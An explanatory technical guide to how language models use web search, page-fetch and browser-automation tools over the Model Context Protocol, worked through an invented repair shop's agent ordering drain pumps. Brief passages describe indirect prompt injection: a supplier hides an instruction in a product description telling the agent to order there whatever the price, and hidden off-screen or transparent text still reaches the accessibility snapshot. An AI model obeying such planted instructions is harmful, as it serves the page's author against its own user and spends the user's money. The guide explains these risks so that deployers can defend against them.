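# Web search, browser and code tools for language models over the Model Context Protocol: how they work, how they fail and how to limit the harm

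## What the tools do and how a model calls them

A large language model is trained on a fixed body of text, so it lacks newer information, such as the current price of a spare part, whether a shop has the part in stock, or what is in a file that a customer sent an hour ago. It also can't act on such information alone, because it only produces output for someone or something else to use. Tools fill both gaps. A tool is a function, such as a web search, that the model can request by name. Ordinary software carries out the request and adds the result to the model's input as text. A model that does this in a loop, using each result to choose the next action, is an agent.

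The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard for the messages between a model's application and its tools. According to @IT's *「MCPはもう特別な存在ではない」*, an article in the Japanese trade press, connecting n models to m services takes up to n × m separate integrations without a shared standard, but closer to n + m with one, because each side implements the protocol once.

Three kinds of MCP tool give a model live access to the web and let it run code. Search and fetch tools return text: a search tool takes a query and returns a list of results, and a fetch tool takes an address and returns the body of the page. Browser tools operate a browser, so the model can log in, click and fill in forms. Many of them give the model a text description of each page taken from the accessibility tree, the outline of roles, names and states that browsers build for screen readers. Code tools take programs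 the model writes and run them in a sandbox, an environment that limits which files, processes and networks a program can reach.

David Soria Parra and Justin Spahr-Summers began building MCP in the summer of 2024, and Anthropic, the company behind the Claude models, released it as open source that November. In March 2025 Microsoft released Playwright MCP, a server that lets a model drive a browser through the company's Playwright automation library. In December 2025 the protocol moved to the Agentic AI Foundation, a vendor-neutral body under the Linux Foundation. In *Two Years of MCP Builders*, Soria Parra and Delimarsky (2026) count 5 billion downloads of the protocol's software development kits, the libraries developers use to build clients and servers. Monthly downloads rose from just over 90 million in November 2025 to more than 700 million a year later. Downloads are a loose measure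 of use, because automated builds fetch the same library repeatedly. Figures for actual calls are rarer. The Agentic AI Foundation's *MCP Usage Surged as the Protocol Went Stateless* (2026) reports that ChatGPT users made 98 times as many tool calls in August 2026 as in January, but gives no absolute number. The Linux Foundation had counted over 10,000 public servers by December 2025, according to @IT, while Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports a little over 950 in Claude's own directory. Most of the servers a deployer can find have probably never been listed there.

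### An order for a spare part

Consider an invented repair shop that needs four drain pumps for a common washing machine. The owner gives the job to an assistant, an agent with all three kinds of tool, and the work goes like this:

1. The assistant searches the web for the part number and finds product pages at three suppliers.
2. It fetches the pages and reads the price at two of them. The third supplier shows trade prices only to customers who log in.
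3. It opens the third supplier's site in a browser and logs in with the shop's account.
4. It downloads that supplier's price list, a spreadsheet of several thousand rows.
5. It writes a short program that finds the pump in the list, applies the quantity discount and adds shipping and tax. The sandbox runs the program.
6. The third supplier turns out to be the cheapest, so the assistant goes back to the browser and fills in the order form. The owner approves the order before it goes out.

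The first two steps only read public pages. From the third step on, the assistant can use the shop's account, and the last step spends the shop's money.

### From the tool list to the result

The host is the application that runs the model, such as a chat program on the owner's computer or a service in a data center. A server is a program that offers tools, and it can run on the same machine or somewhere on the internet. The host creates a client for each server it connects to, a component that communicates only with that server. If separate servers provide search, browser and sandbox, the shop's assistant would need one host with three clients.

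Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), the part of the specification that defines these roles, makes the host responsible for permissions and user consent, and keeps the full conversation there. A server should receive only the information it needs and should not be able to see into other servers. But the model reads the results from all the servers, and the message format does not stop it from copying a line of a web page into a call to the sandbox.

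A model's context is everything it reads before its next output, including text and images. Developers measure context in tokens, the units in which models read and write text. A token is about three quarters of an English word.

To find out which tools are available, the client sends the server a `tools/list` request. The server replies with each tool's name, a plain-language description and an input schema, which formally specifies the arguments the tool accepts. A search tool's schema, for example, might require a single string. The host puts these definitions into the model's context, which is how the model gets its information about the tools. The Playwright documentation advertises more than 70 tools, and each definition the host loads uses tokens before the model has opened a page.

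When the model decides to search, it writes the name of the tool and the arguments. It contacts nothing itself. The client wraps the model's request in JSON-RPC, a simple convention for calling functions on another machine, and sends it. Here is the shop's first search as it would travel over HTTP under the specification of July 28, 2026:

```
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Content-Type: application/json
Mcp-Name: web_search
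Mcp-Method: tools/call
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2026-07-28

{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 1,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "web_search",
    "arguments": { "query": "drain pump DP-40 price" },
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientInfo": {
        "name": "repair-shop-assistant", "version": "1.0"
      },
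      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {}
    }
  }
}
```

The model chose only the tool name and the `arguments`. The client added the `_meta` block. Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) requires this block to include the protocol version and the client's capabilities in every request. The sample call in the release announcement by Model Context Protocol (2026) omits both fields, so a server that follows the specification will return an error to anyone who copies it. The client's name is optional, and nobody verifies it. The specification warns against basing security decisions on it.

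The headers at the top repeat the method and the tool name, so a gateway between client and server can filter calls without reading the body. If the headers and body don't match, the server must reject the request. Otherwise, as the Agentic AI Foundation points out, the gateway could authorize one operation while the server executed another. A local server that communicates with the host through standard input and output gets the JSON without the headers.

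The server runs the search and sends back a result with the same `id` as the request. The result's `content` field holds a list of items, which for a search would be text containing titles, addresses and short extracts. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) also allows images and audio. The host adds the text to the context, alongside the owner's instructions and all the earlier results, and the model uses this context to choose its next action.

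A failed tool call returns one of two kinds of error. If the search service is down or an argument has the wrong format, the result contains `isError: true` and an explanation, which the client should pass to the model so it can correct the call and retry. If the tool does not exist, the call produces a protocol error, which models are less likely to be able to fix. Tool names should be unique within a server, but two servers can both offer `search`, so the host has to tell them apart, for instance with a prefix.

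### What the July 2026 revision changed

Under the previous revision, of November 2025, the same search over HTTP took more than one message. The client began with a handshake, and the server could issue a session identifier that the client had to include in every later request. Busy services run many copies of a server, so operators had to route each client back to the copy that held its session or give all the copies a shared store. The July revision removes both the handshake and the session. Each request now carries what the server needs to process it, so any copy can answer. One reason for the change was scale. *Sessionless MCP via Explicit State Handles* (Alexander, 2026), the proposal that removed sessions, also cites disagreement among clients about what a session meant, which persisted more than a year after sessions entered the specification.

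This matters little for web searches, because each search is independent of the one before. A browser tool, however, has to keep track of which page is open. A server that needs to keep such state now creates a handle, an identifier that it returns in a tool result and that the model passes back as an argument. The protocol treats the handle like any other string. For example, the browser server might return `browser_id: b_7f3a` when it opens a window and require that value in every later call to click or type.

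The maintainers of Model Context Protocol prefer explicit handles to hidden session state because the model can see a handle and pass it from one tool to another. They base this on experience and give no measurements. @IT notes that state kept in the conversation takes up context, and more of it as the task gets longer. A short identifier takes up little, but a few thousand rows of a price list take up a lot, which is a reason to leave the list in a file and give the model only the file's name.

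The Model Context Protocol specification recommends that servers with authentication check on every call whether the caller is allowed to use the handle. On a server without authentication, anyone who has the handle can use the browser it refers to, so the handle should be hard to guess and should expire.

The revision also changes how a tool gets input from the user partway through a call. Suppose the tool that submits the order needs the owner to answer "Order four pumps?" Previously, the server could send its own request to the client while the call was still open. Now it ends the call with an `input_required` result, which contains the question and, optionally, a block of data called `requestState`. The client asks the owner the question, then sends the original call again under a new `id`, with the answer and any `requestState` attached unchanged. Any copy of the server can then finish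 the task.

Model Context Protocol's *Multi Round-Trip Requests* (2026) requires servers to treat the returned `requestState` as if an attacker had written it, and to protect it cryptographically if it affects what the caller may do. A server may ask the user a question only if the client has declared support for that, and the search request above declares none because its `clientCapabilities` is empty. Code from the spring of 2026 also needs checking, because the release candidate that Model Context Protocol announced in May spelled the type `inputRequired`, which the final specification does not define. None of this guarantees that a person sees an order before it goes out, because the server's developer decides whether to ask, and the specification only recommends that hosts let users refuse tool calls.

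Under a change listed in Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), a request is lost if its HTTP response stream breaks off, and the client must send it again as a new request. Repeating a search is harmless, but repeating an order could duplicate it, because the supplier may already have received the first request when the connection failed. A tool that places orders therefore needs its own guard against ordering twice.

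The July revision is current, and *A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP* (Delimarsky and Soria Parra, 2026) sets March 30, 2027 as the target date for the next. In the meantime, deployers should expect some servers to use older revisions. Results from these servers lack the field for the result type, and clients have to accept them anyway.

### Where the browser's state lives

Removing the session from the protocol does not log the assistant out of the supplier's site. Madabhushi (2026), in *MCP sessions are gone. Where should your state live?*, calls migrating an existing server mostly mechanical and finds the question of the application's own state more interesting. After the login in step 3, the supplier recognizes the shop by a cookie, a small piece of data that the site stores in the browser and that the browser returns with each request. The browser that the server controls holds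 this cookie, the open tabs and the half-finished order form. A handle can identify that browser but does not contain its state.

How long the login lasts depends on the configuration. By default, the Playwright server keeps a persistent profile for each project, a folder on disk that keeps cookies and logins between sessions. The repair shop's assistant may therefore still have access to the supplier account tomorrow, when somebody gives it an unrelated job in the same project. The option `--isolated` makes every session start empty. A third mode connects the server to tabs in a browser that the user already has open.

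Browsers keep sites apart by origin, the combination of scheme (such as https), host and port in a site's address. Under the same-origin policy, a script from one origin cannot read another origin's data, so a page at the first supplier cannot read the shop's account at the third. The assistant, however, reads pages from all three suppliers into a single context, where no such rule applies. This makes indirect prompt injection possible, in which an author places instructions in content the agent will read, so that the agent serves the author instead of its user. For example, the first supplier could add a sentence to its product description telling the assistant to order the pumps there, whatever they cost elsewhere.

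## Giving the model search and page fetching

The repair shop's assistant starts with a part number but no web addresses, so it has to search before it can fetch. A search tool returns short excerpts from many pages, usually taken from copies that a search company collected earlier. A fetch tool returns a longer stretch of text from one page, often directly from the site. A price in a search result is therefore less reliable than one on a page the assistant has just fetched.

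### How a search works

A search company runs a crawler, a program that continually downloads web pages, and builds an index from the copies. When a query arrives, the company's software finds matching pages in the index, ranks them and returns the top few. The MCP server then passes on only the fields its developer chose from each result.

Brave, which makes a web browser and runs its own search index, offers an MCP server with a tool called `brave_web_search`. In the June 2026 version, the tool accepts a query of up to 400 characters and 50 words. It returns 10 web results by default and 20 at most. The default country is the United States and the default language is English, so a repair shop in Lyon searching for suppliers may get American ones unless it changes these settings.

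This tool passes the model four fields for each web result: the address, the title, a short description and, on some of Brave's plans, up to five extra excerpts. The model doesn't receive the lower-ranked pages, the reasons for the ranking or any date the search engine holds for a page. A description that gives the pump's price as $31.90 reads the same whether Brave crawled the page this morning or last year. The tool has a `freshness` filter, but it selects pages by when Brave discovered them, so it can exclude a supplier's years-old product page that shows today's price.

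Brave also offers `brave_llm_context`, which returns passages from the pages themselves. Brave says the tool runs an ordinary search on its index, splits the resulting pages into chunks, ranks the chunks and returns the best ones within a token budget. By default, according to Brave's documentation, it considers 20 search results and returns up to about 8,192 tokens, with at most 4,096 from any one page. The tool takes a search query, so the model can't use it to fetch a particular address.

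Deployers should compare the version of the server they run with the current documentation. The June version of this tool lets the model limit the number of excerpts, but Brave has since removed those limits from the service behind the tool. The service still accepts the old parameters and ignores them, so setting them no longer saves context and causes no error message.

*Web Search MCP* describes a server from Exa, another search company, that turns on two tools by default, one for search and one for fetching pages. Exa's listing on AWS, Amazon's cloud marketplace, says its search matches meaning rather than keywords and recommends writing queries as descriptions of the page wanted. Part numbers could be difficult for this kind of search, because DP-40 and DP-41 mean nearly the same thing but may fit different machines. The assistant should check the exact number on the page it uses.

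Deployers choose Exa's tools by listing them in the server's address. Exa notes that this list replaces the default tools, which is also easy to miss. Someone who lists only the advanced search tool loses the fetch tool.

### How a fetch works

Model Context Protocol's *Fetch MCP Server* describes the project's own reference server, a small program that many others imitate. When the model calls its `fetch` tool, the server does the following:

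1. It checks that the address is a public one and that the site's robots.txt file permits the request. In this file, a site's owner states which pages automated visitors may load.
2. It requests the page. If the site redirects the request to another address, the server makes both checks again for the new address.
3. It extracts the main content from the HTML, the code that describes a web page, and converts it to Markdown, a plain-text format that marks headings, links and tables with a few characters.
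4. It returns 5,000 characters of the result, starting from the beginning.

The model can change the amount of text with `max_length` and the starting point with `start_index`, so it can read a long page in pieces. In a Rust version, documented in Docs.rs' *mcp-server-fetch 0.1.0*, a truncated result ends with the offset for the next call, so the model knows there is more to read. Exa's fetch tool has a lower default of 3,000 characters per page, according to the tool directory Claude Marketplaces, but it accepts several addresses in one call.

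If the machine has Node.js, a program for running JavaScript outside a browser, the reference server converts pages with a different extractor, which the server's maintainers call more robust. Two installations of the same server can therefore get different text from the same page.

The reference server obeys a site's robots.txt when the model calls the fetch tool, but not when a user starts the fetch through a prompt, a ready-made command that the server offers in the host's menu. It identifies itself to the site as "Autonomous" in the first case and "User-Specified" in the second. A deployer can switch off the robots.txt check with `--ignore-robots-txt`, and Glama's *MCP Fetch* lists a public copy of the server whose developer removed the check altogether. Brave's guide to its passage search and Exa's guide to page contents don't mention robots.txt, so a deployer who must respect site owners'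 wishes has to ask those companies how their crawlers behave.

When robots.txt forbids a fetch, a site is unreachable or an address is blocked, the model gets an error it can read, so it can try another page. In the shop's case, it is often better for the model to tell the owner that one supplier is missing from the comparison.

### What the comparison costs in tokens

The counts below are illustrative. They are based on four characters per token, 80 tokens per search result and a first supplier whose long product description pushes the price past the 5,000-character mark. They exclude the owner's instructions and the tool definitions.

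| Step | Tokens added | Tokens in context afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| Search, ten results | 800 | 800 |
| Fetch the first supplier's page | 1,250 | 2,050 |
| Fetch the same page from character 5,000 | 1,250 | 3,300 |
| Fetch the second supplier's page | 1,250 | 4,550 |

The model reads the whole context again before each output. It reads 800 tokens before the first fetch, 2,050 before the second, 3,300 before the third and 4,550 before it reports the prices. In total it reads 10,700 tokens to process 4,550 tokens of text, although many providers charge less for text they have recently processed.

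A higher `max_length` would save a step. If the assistant had asked for 10,000 characters of the first page, it would have added the same 2,500 tokens in one call and read 8,650 tokens in total. But the same setting on the second page could add 1,250 tokens of delivery terms and customer reviews that it doesn't need. Raw HTML would use far more tokens. A product page with 300,000 characters of code would take 75,000 tokens to read in full, and its first 5,000 characters might all be part of the page's header.

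### Choices in setting up search

A stored copy of a page arrives quickly and doesn't depend on the site being up, but it may be out of date. Exa's *Livecrawling Contents*, an older guide, gives the causes of the Second World War as a topic for which a stored copy is good enough. Exa recommends leaving its freshness setting, `maxAgeHours`, alone for most requests and using it where stale content would be unusable, as with prices and availability. According to Exa's *February 2026 API Updates* (2026), a value of 24 reloads the page if the copy is more than a day old, 0 always reloads it and -1 uses only the stored copy. Even with 0, a repeated request within 60 seconds can return the same copy.

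Other providers make similar compromises. According to Firecrawl's *Fast Scraping*, its service returns copies up to two days old by default. Forcing a fresh load takes longer and fails more often. Brave's passage search also returns cached content by default. It tries to provide uncached content on request, but can't always do so.

A freshness setting helps only if the MCP tool exposes it. Claude Marketplaces lists two parameters for Exa's fetch tool, the addresses and the maximum number of characters. The assistant can't request a live page with that version of the tool, even though Exa's API allows it. It makes sense for the repair shop to find the suppliers through an index and then read the prices with a tool that loads pages live.

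Exa recommends excerpts for agents because they take up less context. Excerpts work well when the answer is a single fact in one place, but a price often depends on details elsewhere on the page. The figure may be at the top while the minimum order, the shipping charge or the words "excluding tax" are at the bottom, and an excerpt that matches the query "drain pump price" can easily leave those out. The shop should use excerpts to choose pages and full text for the pages whose figures go into the order.

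**The model's platform or a separate server.** A company that hosts models can also run the search. Google Cloud's *Grounding with Parallel Web Search* explains how a developer selects an outside search company, Parallel, in the settings, and the platform then adds search results to the model's responses. Google Cloud's *Grounding with Exa web search* describes the same arrangement with Exa and claims better accuracy and fewer hallucinations (statements the model makes up). This saves the developer from running or connecting a server. With a separate MCP server, every query and result passes through the host, which can log them, block some or switch to another search company without changing the model. That control is probably worth the extra work for an assistant that also holds a supplier's login.

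**One search or several.** Brave said in 2025 that answers on its own site, based on a single search, appeared in under 4.5 seconds on average. Repeated searches cost more because they involve more calls, text and reasoning, but they find pages that the first wording missed. Exa instructs agents to run two or three differently worded queries for broad topics and merge the results. A search for a part number is narrow, so one query may be enough. A second makes sense if the manufacturer has renumbered the part or if the first returned only auction listings.

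Repeated searches can also reach a usage limit. In February 2026, Exa allowed users without an account 150 calls a day to its MCP server. At four calls per comparison, as in the table, the shop could complete 37 comparisons a day and would reach the limit partway through the 38th.

### What search adds to measured ability

Search clearly helps a model look up a current price. Researchers have mostly tested a harder task, which is finding facts that are on the web but difficult to locate. The best-known test is BrowseComp, which OpenAI released in April 2025. *Improving and Evaluating Open Deep Research Agents* (2025) describes its 1,266 questions, on subjects from entertainment to geography, as hard to solve but with short answers that are easy to verify. A question might give several vague clues about a short-lived television series and ask for its title. It can take dozens of searches to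 find the title but only a few to check it.

At the launch, OpenAI's Wei and colleagues reported that GPT-4o answered 0.6 percent of the questions correctly without browsing and 1.9 percent with it, a gain of about 16 questions out of 1,266. OpenAI's o1, a model trained to reason at length, reached 9.9 percent without browsing. Deep Research, an OpenAI agent trained to search persistently, reached 51.5 percent. So in spring 2025, web access did little for a model that hadn't learned to use it well.

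Those scores are out of date, and the way the questions were chosen also lowered them. The question writers checked that ChatGPT, with and without browsing, and an early version of Deep Research could not solve them. A test built from questions that a system has failed will understate how useful the system is on ordinary questions. The results are therefore a poor guide to a job like the repair shop's, where the first search will often return the right page.

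BrowseComp scores can also differ for reasons unrelated to the agents, because the live web and search rankings change between runs. *BrowseComp-Plus* (2025) removes this problem by using a fixed collection of documents. For each question, the collection contains documents that people have verified as supporting the answer, along with misleading ones that look relevant. The fixed collection also made it possible to keep the agent the same and change only the retriever, the component that finds documents for a query. Better retrievers made the answers more accurate and reduced the number of searches. A simulated perfect retriever raised accuracy considerably further, so the agents had been getting many questions wrong because they never received the right document.

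This finding is more useful to a deployer because it suggests that a better search service can improve an agent without any change to the model, and can offset some of its own cost because the agent makes fewer calls. The evidence comes from a closed collection and difficult questions, though, so a shop choosing between two search companies would learn more by running 50 of its own past part numbers through both.

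Agents can also search such a collection without an index. *Beyond Semantic Similarity* (2026) tests agents that search the BrowseComp-Plus documents using terminal commands instead. The shop's assistant will later look for a row in a downloaded price list in much the same way. To save money, the researchers used a random sample of 50 questions from the benchmark. At a score near 50 percent, a sample of that size has a margin of error of about plus or minus 14 percentage points, compared with about 3 points for the full BrowseComp. Small differences between agents on samples like this therefore mean very little.

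### How failures appear

**Citations may not support the claim.** Brave instructs models using its passage search to cite web addresses from the result's list of sources, and Exa instructs agents to give an address for every fact, but neither company's tool compares the claim with the cited page. The assistant might cite one supplier's page for another supplier's price, or cite the correct page but give the price of a pack of two as the price of a single item. In both cases the link works and the answer looks well sourced.

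The host can catch some of these errors with ordinary code. If it stores the text of every fetched page, it can check that each cited address was among the results and that the quoted figure appears in that page's text. These checks would catch the swapped suppliers but not the pack of two, so somebody should still open the page before a large order.

**Stale copies.** An old price looks the same as a current one. Brave's passage search can return the time at which its index last fetched a page, but only if the caller sets `enable_source_metadata`, which is off by default. Firecrawl's *Verifying Freshness and Liveness* distinguishes between a recent copy and a page whose content is still true. A supplier may leave "in stock" on a page for days after selling the last pump, so even a copy fetched one second ago can be wrong. The supplier's order form gives better evidence, because it usually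 checks the stock and the price again.

**Text lost in conversion.** Extractors try to keep the main content and discard clutter such as menus and advertisements. They work best on articles. On a product page, they may discard the box that contains the price or turn a table of quantity discounts into a row of unlabeled numbers. Crossed-out prices are a particular risk, because an old price of $39.90 with a line through it and the new price of $31.90 may arrive as two plain numbers. If a figure is missing or ambiguous, the assistant can fetch the page again with `raw` set to true and look for the price in the HTML.

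**Pages that need JavaScript.** Many shops send a nearly empty page and let a script in the visitor's browser load the price. The reference server doesn't run a page's scripts, so it may return only a heading, a menu and the word "Loading". Because the request succeeded, the result carries no error, and the model may wrongly report that the supplier lists no price. Exa says its service handles such pages. Running scripts still wouldn't get the third supplier's trade prices, because the fetch tool isn't logged in to the shop's account and gets the login form instead, so the assistant needs a browser for that supplier.

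## Driving a browser through accessibility snapshots

The assistant has to log in to read the third supplier's trade prices and fill in a form to order the pumps. Playwright MCP gives it a browser for both jobs. The server sends the model a snapshot of each page, which is the page's accessibility tree written out as text. Elements in the snapshot have short labels called refs, such as `e5`. The model clicks a button by putting the button's ref in a tool call.

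### From HTML to a snapshot

A browser parses a page's HTML into a document tree, in which a form contains its fields and a list contains its items. Scripts on the page can then change this tree, for instance by adding a price that wasn't in the HTML. The browser builds the accessibility tree from the document tree. *Accessible Name and Description Computation 1.2* (2026), a draft from W3C, the web's main standards body, describes the objects in the accessibility tree. Each object has a role, such as button or heading, and may have states, such as checked or disabled. It can also have a name, a short label that conveys its purpose to the user.

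The server writes the accessibility tree as indented text and adds the refs. Because the browser runs the page's scripts, the snapshot can include prices that the reference fetch server misses.

The table shows the HTML for each element of the third supplier's order form beside a simplified version of its snapshot line. In the full snapshot, the form's contents are indented under the line for the form.

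| HTML | Snapshot |
|---|---|
| `<h1>Quick order</h1>` | `heading "Quick order" [level=1] [ref=e3]` |
| `<form aria-label="Order line">` | `form "Order line" [ref=e4]:` |
| `<label for="part">Part number</label>` | `text: Part number` |
| `<input id="part" type="text">` | `textbox "Part number" [ref=e6]` |
| `<label for="qty">Quantity</label>` | `text: Quantity` |
| `<input id="qty" type="text" value="1">` | `textbox "Quantity" [ref=e8]: "1"` |
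| `<input id="split" type="checkbox" checked>` | `checkbox "Allow split delivery" [checked] [ref=e9]` |
| `<label for="split">Allow split delivery</label>` | `text: Allow split delivery` |
| `<button>Check price</button>` | `button "Check price" [ref=e11]` |

Playwright's *Snapshot testing* explains the format. The role comes first, then the name in quotation marks, then any states in square brackets. A text box's current value follows the colon, so the quantity is 1 and the part number is still empty.

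The quantity field has no text of its own, so the browser looks elsewhere for its name. It starts with ARIA, a set of HTML attributes that developers use to describe elements to screen readers. `aria-labelledby` points to another element whose text serves as the name, and `aria-label` contains the name itself. This field has neither, but it has a `<label>` whose `for="qty"` matches the field's `id`, so the label's text, "Quantity", becomes the name. The button needs no label because a button can take its name from its content.

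This order of precedence can produce a name that differs from what people see. If the supplier's developer had added `aria-label="Packs"` to the quantity field, its name in the snapshot would be "Packs" while the text beside it still read "Quantity". Gray example text inside a box can also supply its name, according to WebAIM, an accessibility organization. A box without a label might appear as `textbox "e.g. DP-40"`, and a model could wrongly treat it as already containing the part number.

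W3C's rules normally keep an element out of the tree if it is hidden with the style `display:none` or the attribute `aria-hidden="true"`. Attackers can exploit the rules because transparent text and text positioned off the screen are still included.

Browser tools get this information in different ways. Chrome for Developers' *Puppetaria* explains that Puppeteer, another automation library, could either query the browser's own accessibility tree or run a script in the page that works from the document tree. Older Playwright source code uses such a script. Two tools can produce different snapshots of the same page, so a deployer who switches tools should check the important pages again.

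### The action loop

Playwright's *Getting Started* describes a cycle of navigating, reading a snapshot, acting and reading the next snapshot. In practice, the agent also has to choose an element and sometimes wait:

1. The model calls `browser_navigate` with an address, and the server returns a snapshot of the page.
2. The model reads the snapshot and chooses an element, such as the text box "Quantity" with the ref `e8`.
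3. It calls a tool such as `browser_click` or `browser_type`, with the ref as the `target`.
4. The server performs the action in the browser and returns a new snapshot.
5. If the page is still loading something, the model calls `browser_wait_for`, which waits for a piece of text or a length of time.
6. The model reads the latest snapshot and chooses its next action.

Agents can easily skip the wait. The supplier's site might take two seconds to look up a price after a click. A snapshot taken during that time accurately describes an unfinished page, and the model may conclude that the supplier has no price. Waiting for text such as "Subtotal" is usually better than waiting for a fixed time, because nobody knows how long the lookup will take.

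According to Playwright's *Snapshots*, the server gives a ref to every node the accessibility tree exposes, including headings and lists. A ref is unique within one snapshot and valid until the page changes. If the server can't find a ref, the tool fails and returns an instruction to try capturing a new snapshot.

Some older instructions no longer match the server. Playwright's guide to its separate command-line tool still describes refs as belonging only to interactive elements, such as buttons and links. An older copy of Playwright's *Interaction* calls the argument `ref`, but the current tools require `target`. A model gets the right name from the tool list, unless the deployer has copied an old example into the model's instructions.

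**Iframes.** A page can contain an iframe, which is another page embedded in it. A supplier might use one for a payment company's card form. Refs for elements in an iframe start with a frame label, so `f1e12` is an element in the first iframe. The model uses these refs like any others. One snapshot can therefore contain text from several companies, even though the browser's same-origin policy stops their scripts from reading each other's pages.

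**Selectors.** The `target` can also be a selector, a pattern that describes the element, such as `getByRole('button', { name: 'Submit' })`. A model that already knows the page can use a selector without reading a snapshot first. Playwright recommends refs over CSS selectors because a ref points to the exact element the model has just read about, while CSS selectors often depend on the page's layout or styling. For a button that spends money, however, a selector based on role and name has an advantage because the server has to find a button named "Place order" at the moment of the click. A ref such as `e24` contains no description for the server to check.

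### Large pages

Suppose the supplier's catalog page lists 400 parts, and each row takes about 200 characters with its cells, button and refs written out. At four characters per token, one snapshot of the page uses about 20,000 tokens. Most tools return a fresh snapshot after each action, so three clicks on this page could add 60,000 more.

The server offers several ways to reduce this, but each can hide something the agent needs:

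| Option | What the model gets | What can go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| `browser_find` | Matching nodes with their refs and a few lines of context | It can't find rows that the site hasn't loaded yet |
| `browser_snapshot` with `target` | One element and everything inside it | The model misses a warning elsewhere on the page |
| `browser_snapshot` with `depth` | Only the upper levels of the tree | A button further down doesn't appear |
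| `browser_snapshot` with `filename` | A file instead of text in the response | The model needs another tool to read the file |
| `--snapshot-mode=none` | No automatic snapshots after actions | The model may act on old information |

`browser_find` is the obvious choice for finding a single part. It accepts plain text or a regular expression, which is a pattern for matching text. A plain-text search ignores case and matches inside longer words, so "DP-40" also finds "DP-400". The regular expression `DP-40\b` excludes the longer number because `\b` requires the word to end there.

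If the agent doesn't know what to search for, it can take a shallow snapshot to find the right region and then request only that region in full. Playwright's guide to its command-line tool recommends this for deep pages, and the MCP server has the same two options. The model shouldn't assume an element is missing from the page just because it's missing from a partial snapshot.

### The order form, call by call

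The assistant has logged in, read the trade price of $27.40 and worked out that the third supplier is the cheapest. It opens the order form with `browser_navigate` and gets the snapshot shown earlier. One call to `browser_fill_form` can complete several fields, and a second call asks the site for the price:

```
browser_fill_form { fields: [
  { name: "Part number", target: "e6",
    type: "textbox", value: "DP-40" },
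  { name: "Quantity", target: "e8",
    type: "textbox", value: "4" },
  { name: "Allow split delivery", target: "e9",
    type: "checkbox", value: "false" }
] }

browser_click { target: "e11" }
```

The `name` in each field is a readable description that doesn't have to match the name in the snapshot. An example in Playwright's *Forms* uses "Subscribe" for a checkbox named "Subscribe to newsletter". The deployer therefore shouldn't rely on `name` to catch a wrong ref.

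After the click, the snapshot contains the text "Checking stock" and a new button, "Review order", with the ref `e14`. The assistant clicks the button without waiting. By then the site has finished its check and replaced the whole form, so the call fails:

```
browser_click { target: "e14" }

Ref e14 not found in the current page snapshot.
Try capturing new snapshot.
```

The assistant calls `browser_snapshot` and gets the new form:

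```
- form "Order line" [ref=e16]:
  - textbox "Part number" [ref=e18]: DP-40
  - textbox "Quantity" [ref=e20]: "1"
  - text: Subtotal $27.40
  - button "Review order" [ref=e24]
```

The button is now `e24`, but the site has also reset the quantity to 1. If the assistant only looked up the new ref and repeated the click, it would go on to order one pump. It has to read the whole form again. It types 4 into `e20`, waits for the subtotal to change to $109.60 and then clicks the button:

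```
browser_type { target: "e20", text: "4" }
browser_wait_for { text: "$109.60" }
browser_click { target: "e24" }

### Modal state
- ["confirm" dialog with message "Add 1 more pump
  for free shipping?"]: can be handled by
  browser_handle_dialog
```

The site has opened a browser dialog, a small window that blocks the page until the user answers. According to Playwright's *Dialogs*, no other tool can run while a dialog is open, so the assistant can't take a snapshot or click anything. An agent that accepts dialogs to get past them would order five pumps. The assistant calls `browser_handle_dialog` with `accept: false` and then takes a new snapshot. The review page lists four DP-40 pumps, no split delivery and a button named "Place order". The assistant asks the owner for approval.

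File choosers block the page in the same way, but the agent clears them with `browser_file_upload`. Pop-ups that a site draws with ordinary HTML appear in the snapshot as part of the page, and the other tools keep working. A site may mark everything behind such a pop-up as inert, which means it doesn't respond to the user. According to Playwright's *Release notes*, from version 1.65 of the library a click on an inert element waits and eventually times out. An agent that gets a timeout on a button should look for an open pop-up before trying the button again.

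### Old refs that still work

The assistant got an error because the new page had no element with the ref `e14`. If it had, the server might have clicked that element instead. In Playwright's example of a two-page registration form, `e7` is the "Next" button on the first page and a checkbox for subscribing to a newsletter on the second. An agent that clicked `e7` again, perhaps because the first click seemed to have failed, could subscribe the user without getting an error.

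The example may be simplified and doesn't prove that the current server makes this mistake, but current refs contain no snapshot number that would rule it out. Earlier Playwright code used refs such as `s1e3`, where `s1` identified the snapshot, and rejected that ref once a second snapshot existed.

Chrome Relay, a similar tool that lets agents control a browser, has made the mistake on a real page. Its developers report that it used an old ref after the page had changed, clicked an unrelated link and counted the click as a success. Chrome had reused the number behind the ref for an element on the new page. Chrome Relay now discards all refs when the browser moves to a new page.

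If only part of a page changes, Chrome Relay looks for the replaced element by its role, name and position, and uses the new one. This avoids many failed calls. But it could have clicked the new "Review order" button on the pump order without the assistant reading that the quantity had gone back to 1. Playwright's error requires an extra call but prompts the assistant to look at the form again.

For these reasons, an agent shouldn't plan several clicks from one snapshot if any of them might change the page. It can fill in several fields together, but it should read the new snapshot before it presses the next button.

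### What the tree leaves out

The accessibility tree is only as accurate and complete as the site's markup. Playwright's *Vision Mode* lists cases where an agent may need screenshots instead, including maps, charts, image editors and custom controls without ARIA. These gaps rarely cause an error, so a deployer has to recognize them from the agent's behavior.

A canvas is an area of the page where a script draws individual pixels. A supplier might use one for a diagram of a washing machine, where customers click on the part they need. The browser has a record of the canvas but not of the shapes drawn on it, so the snapshot doesn't show that one of them is a pump. An agent that reads only the snapshot may search the rest of the page repeatedly or report that the supplier doesn't stock the part.

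A button that shows only a trash can icon, with no text alternative, may appear in the snapshot as `button [ref=e31]`. If the buttons for saving and duplicating an order are also unnamed, the model has to guess which is which. In a log, this looks like a series of clicks on unnamed buttons, each followed by an attempt to undo the result. Guessing is especially dangerous if one of the buttons deletes something.

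In Playwright's example of a solution, the agent takes a screenshot, finds a gear icon about 850 pixels from the left and 45 from the top, and clicks that point with `browser_mouse_click_xy`. The next snapshot shows the settings panel with names and refs, so the agent can go back to using refs. The coordinate tools are available only if the deployer starts the server with `--caps=vision`.

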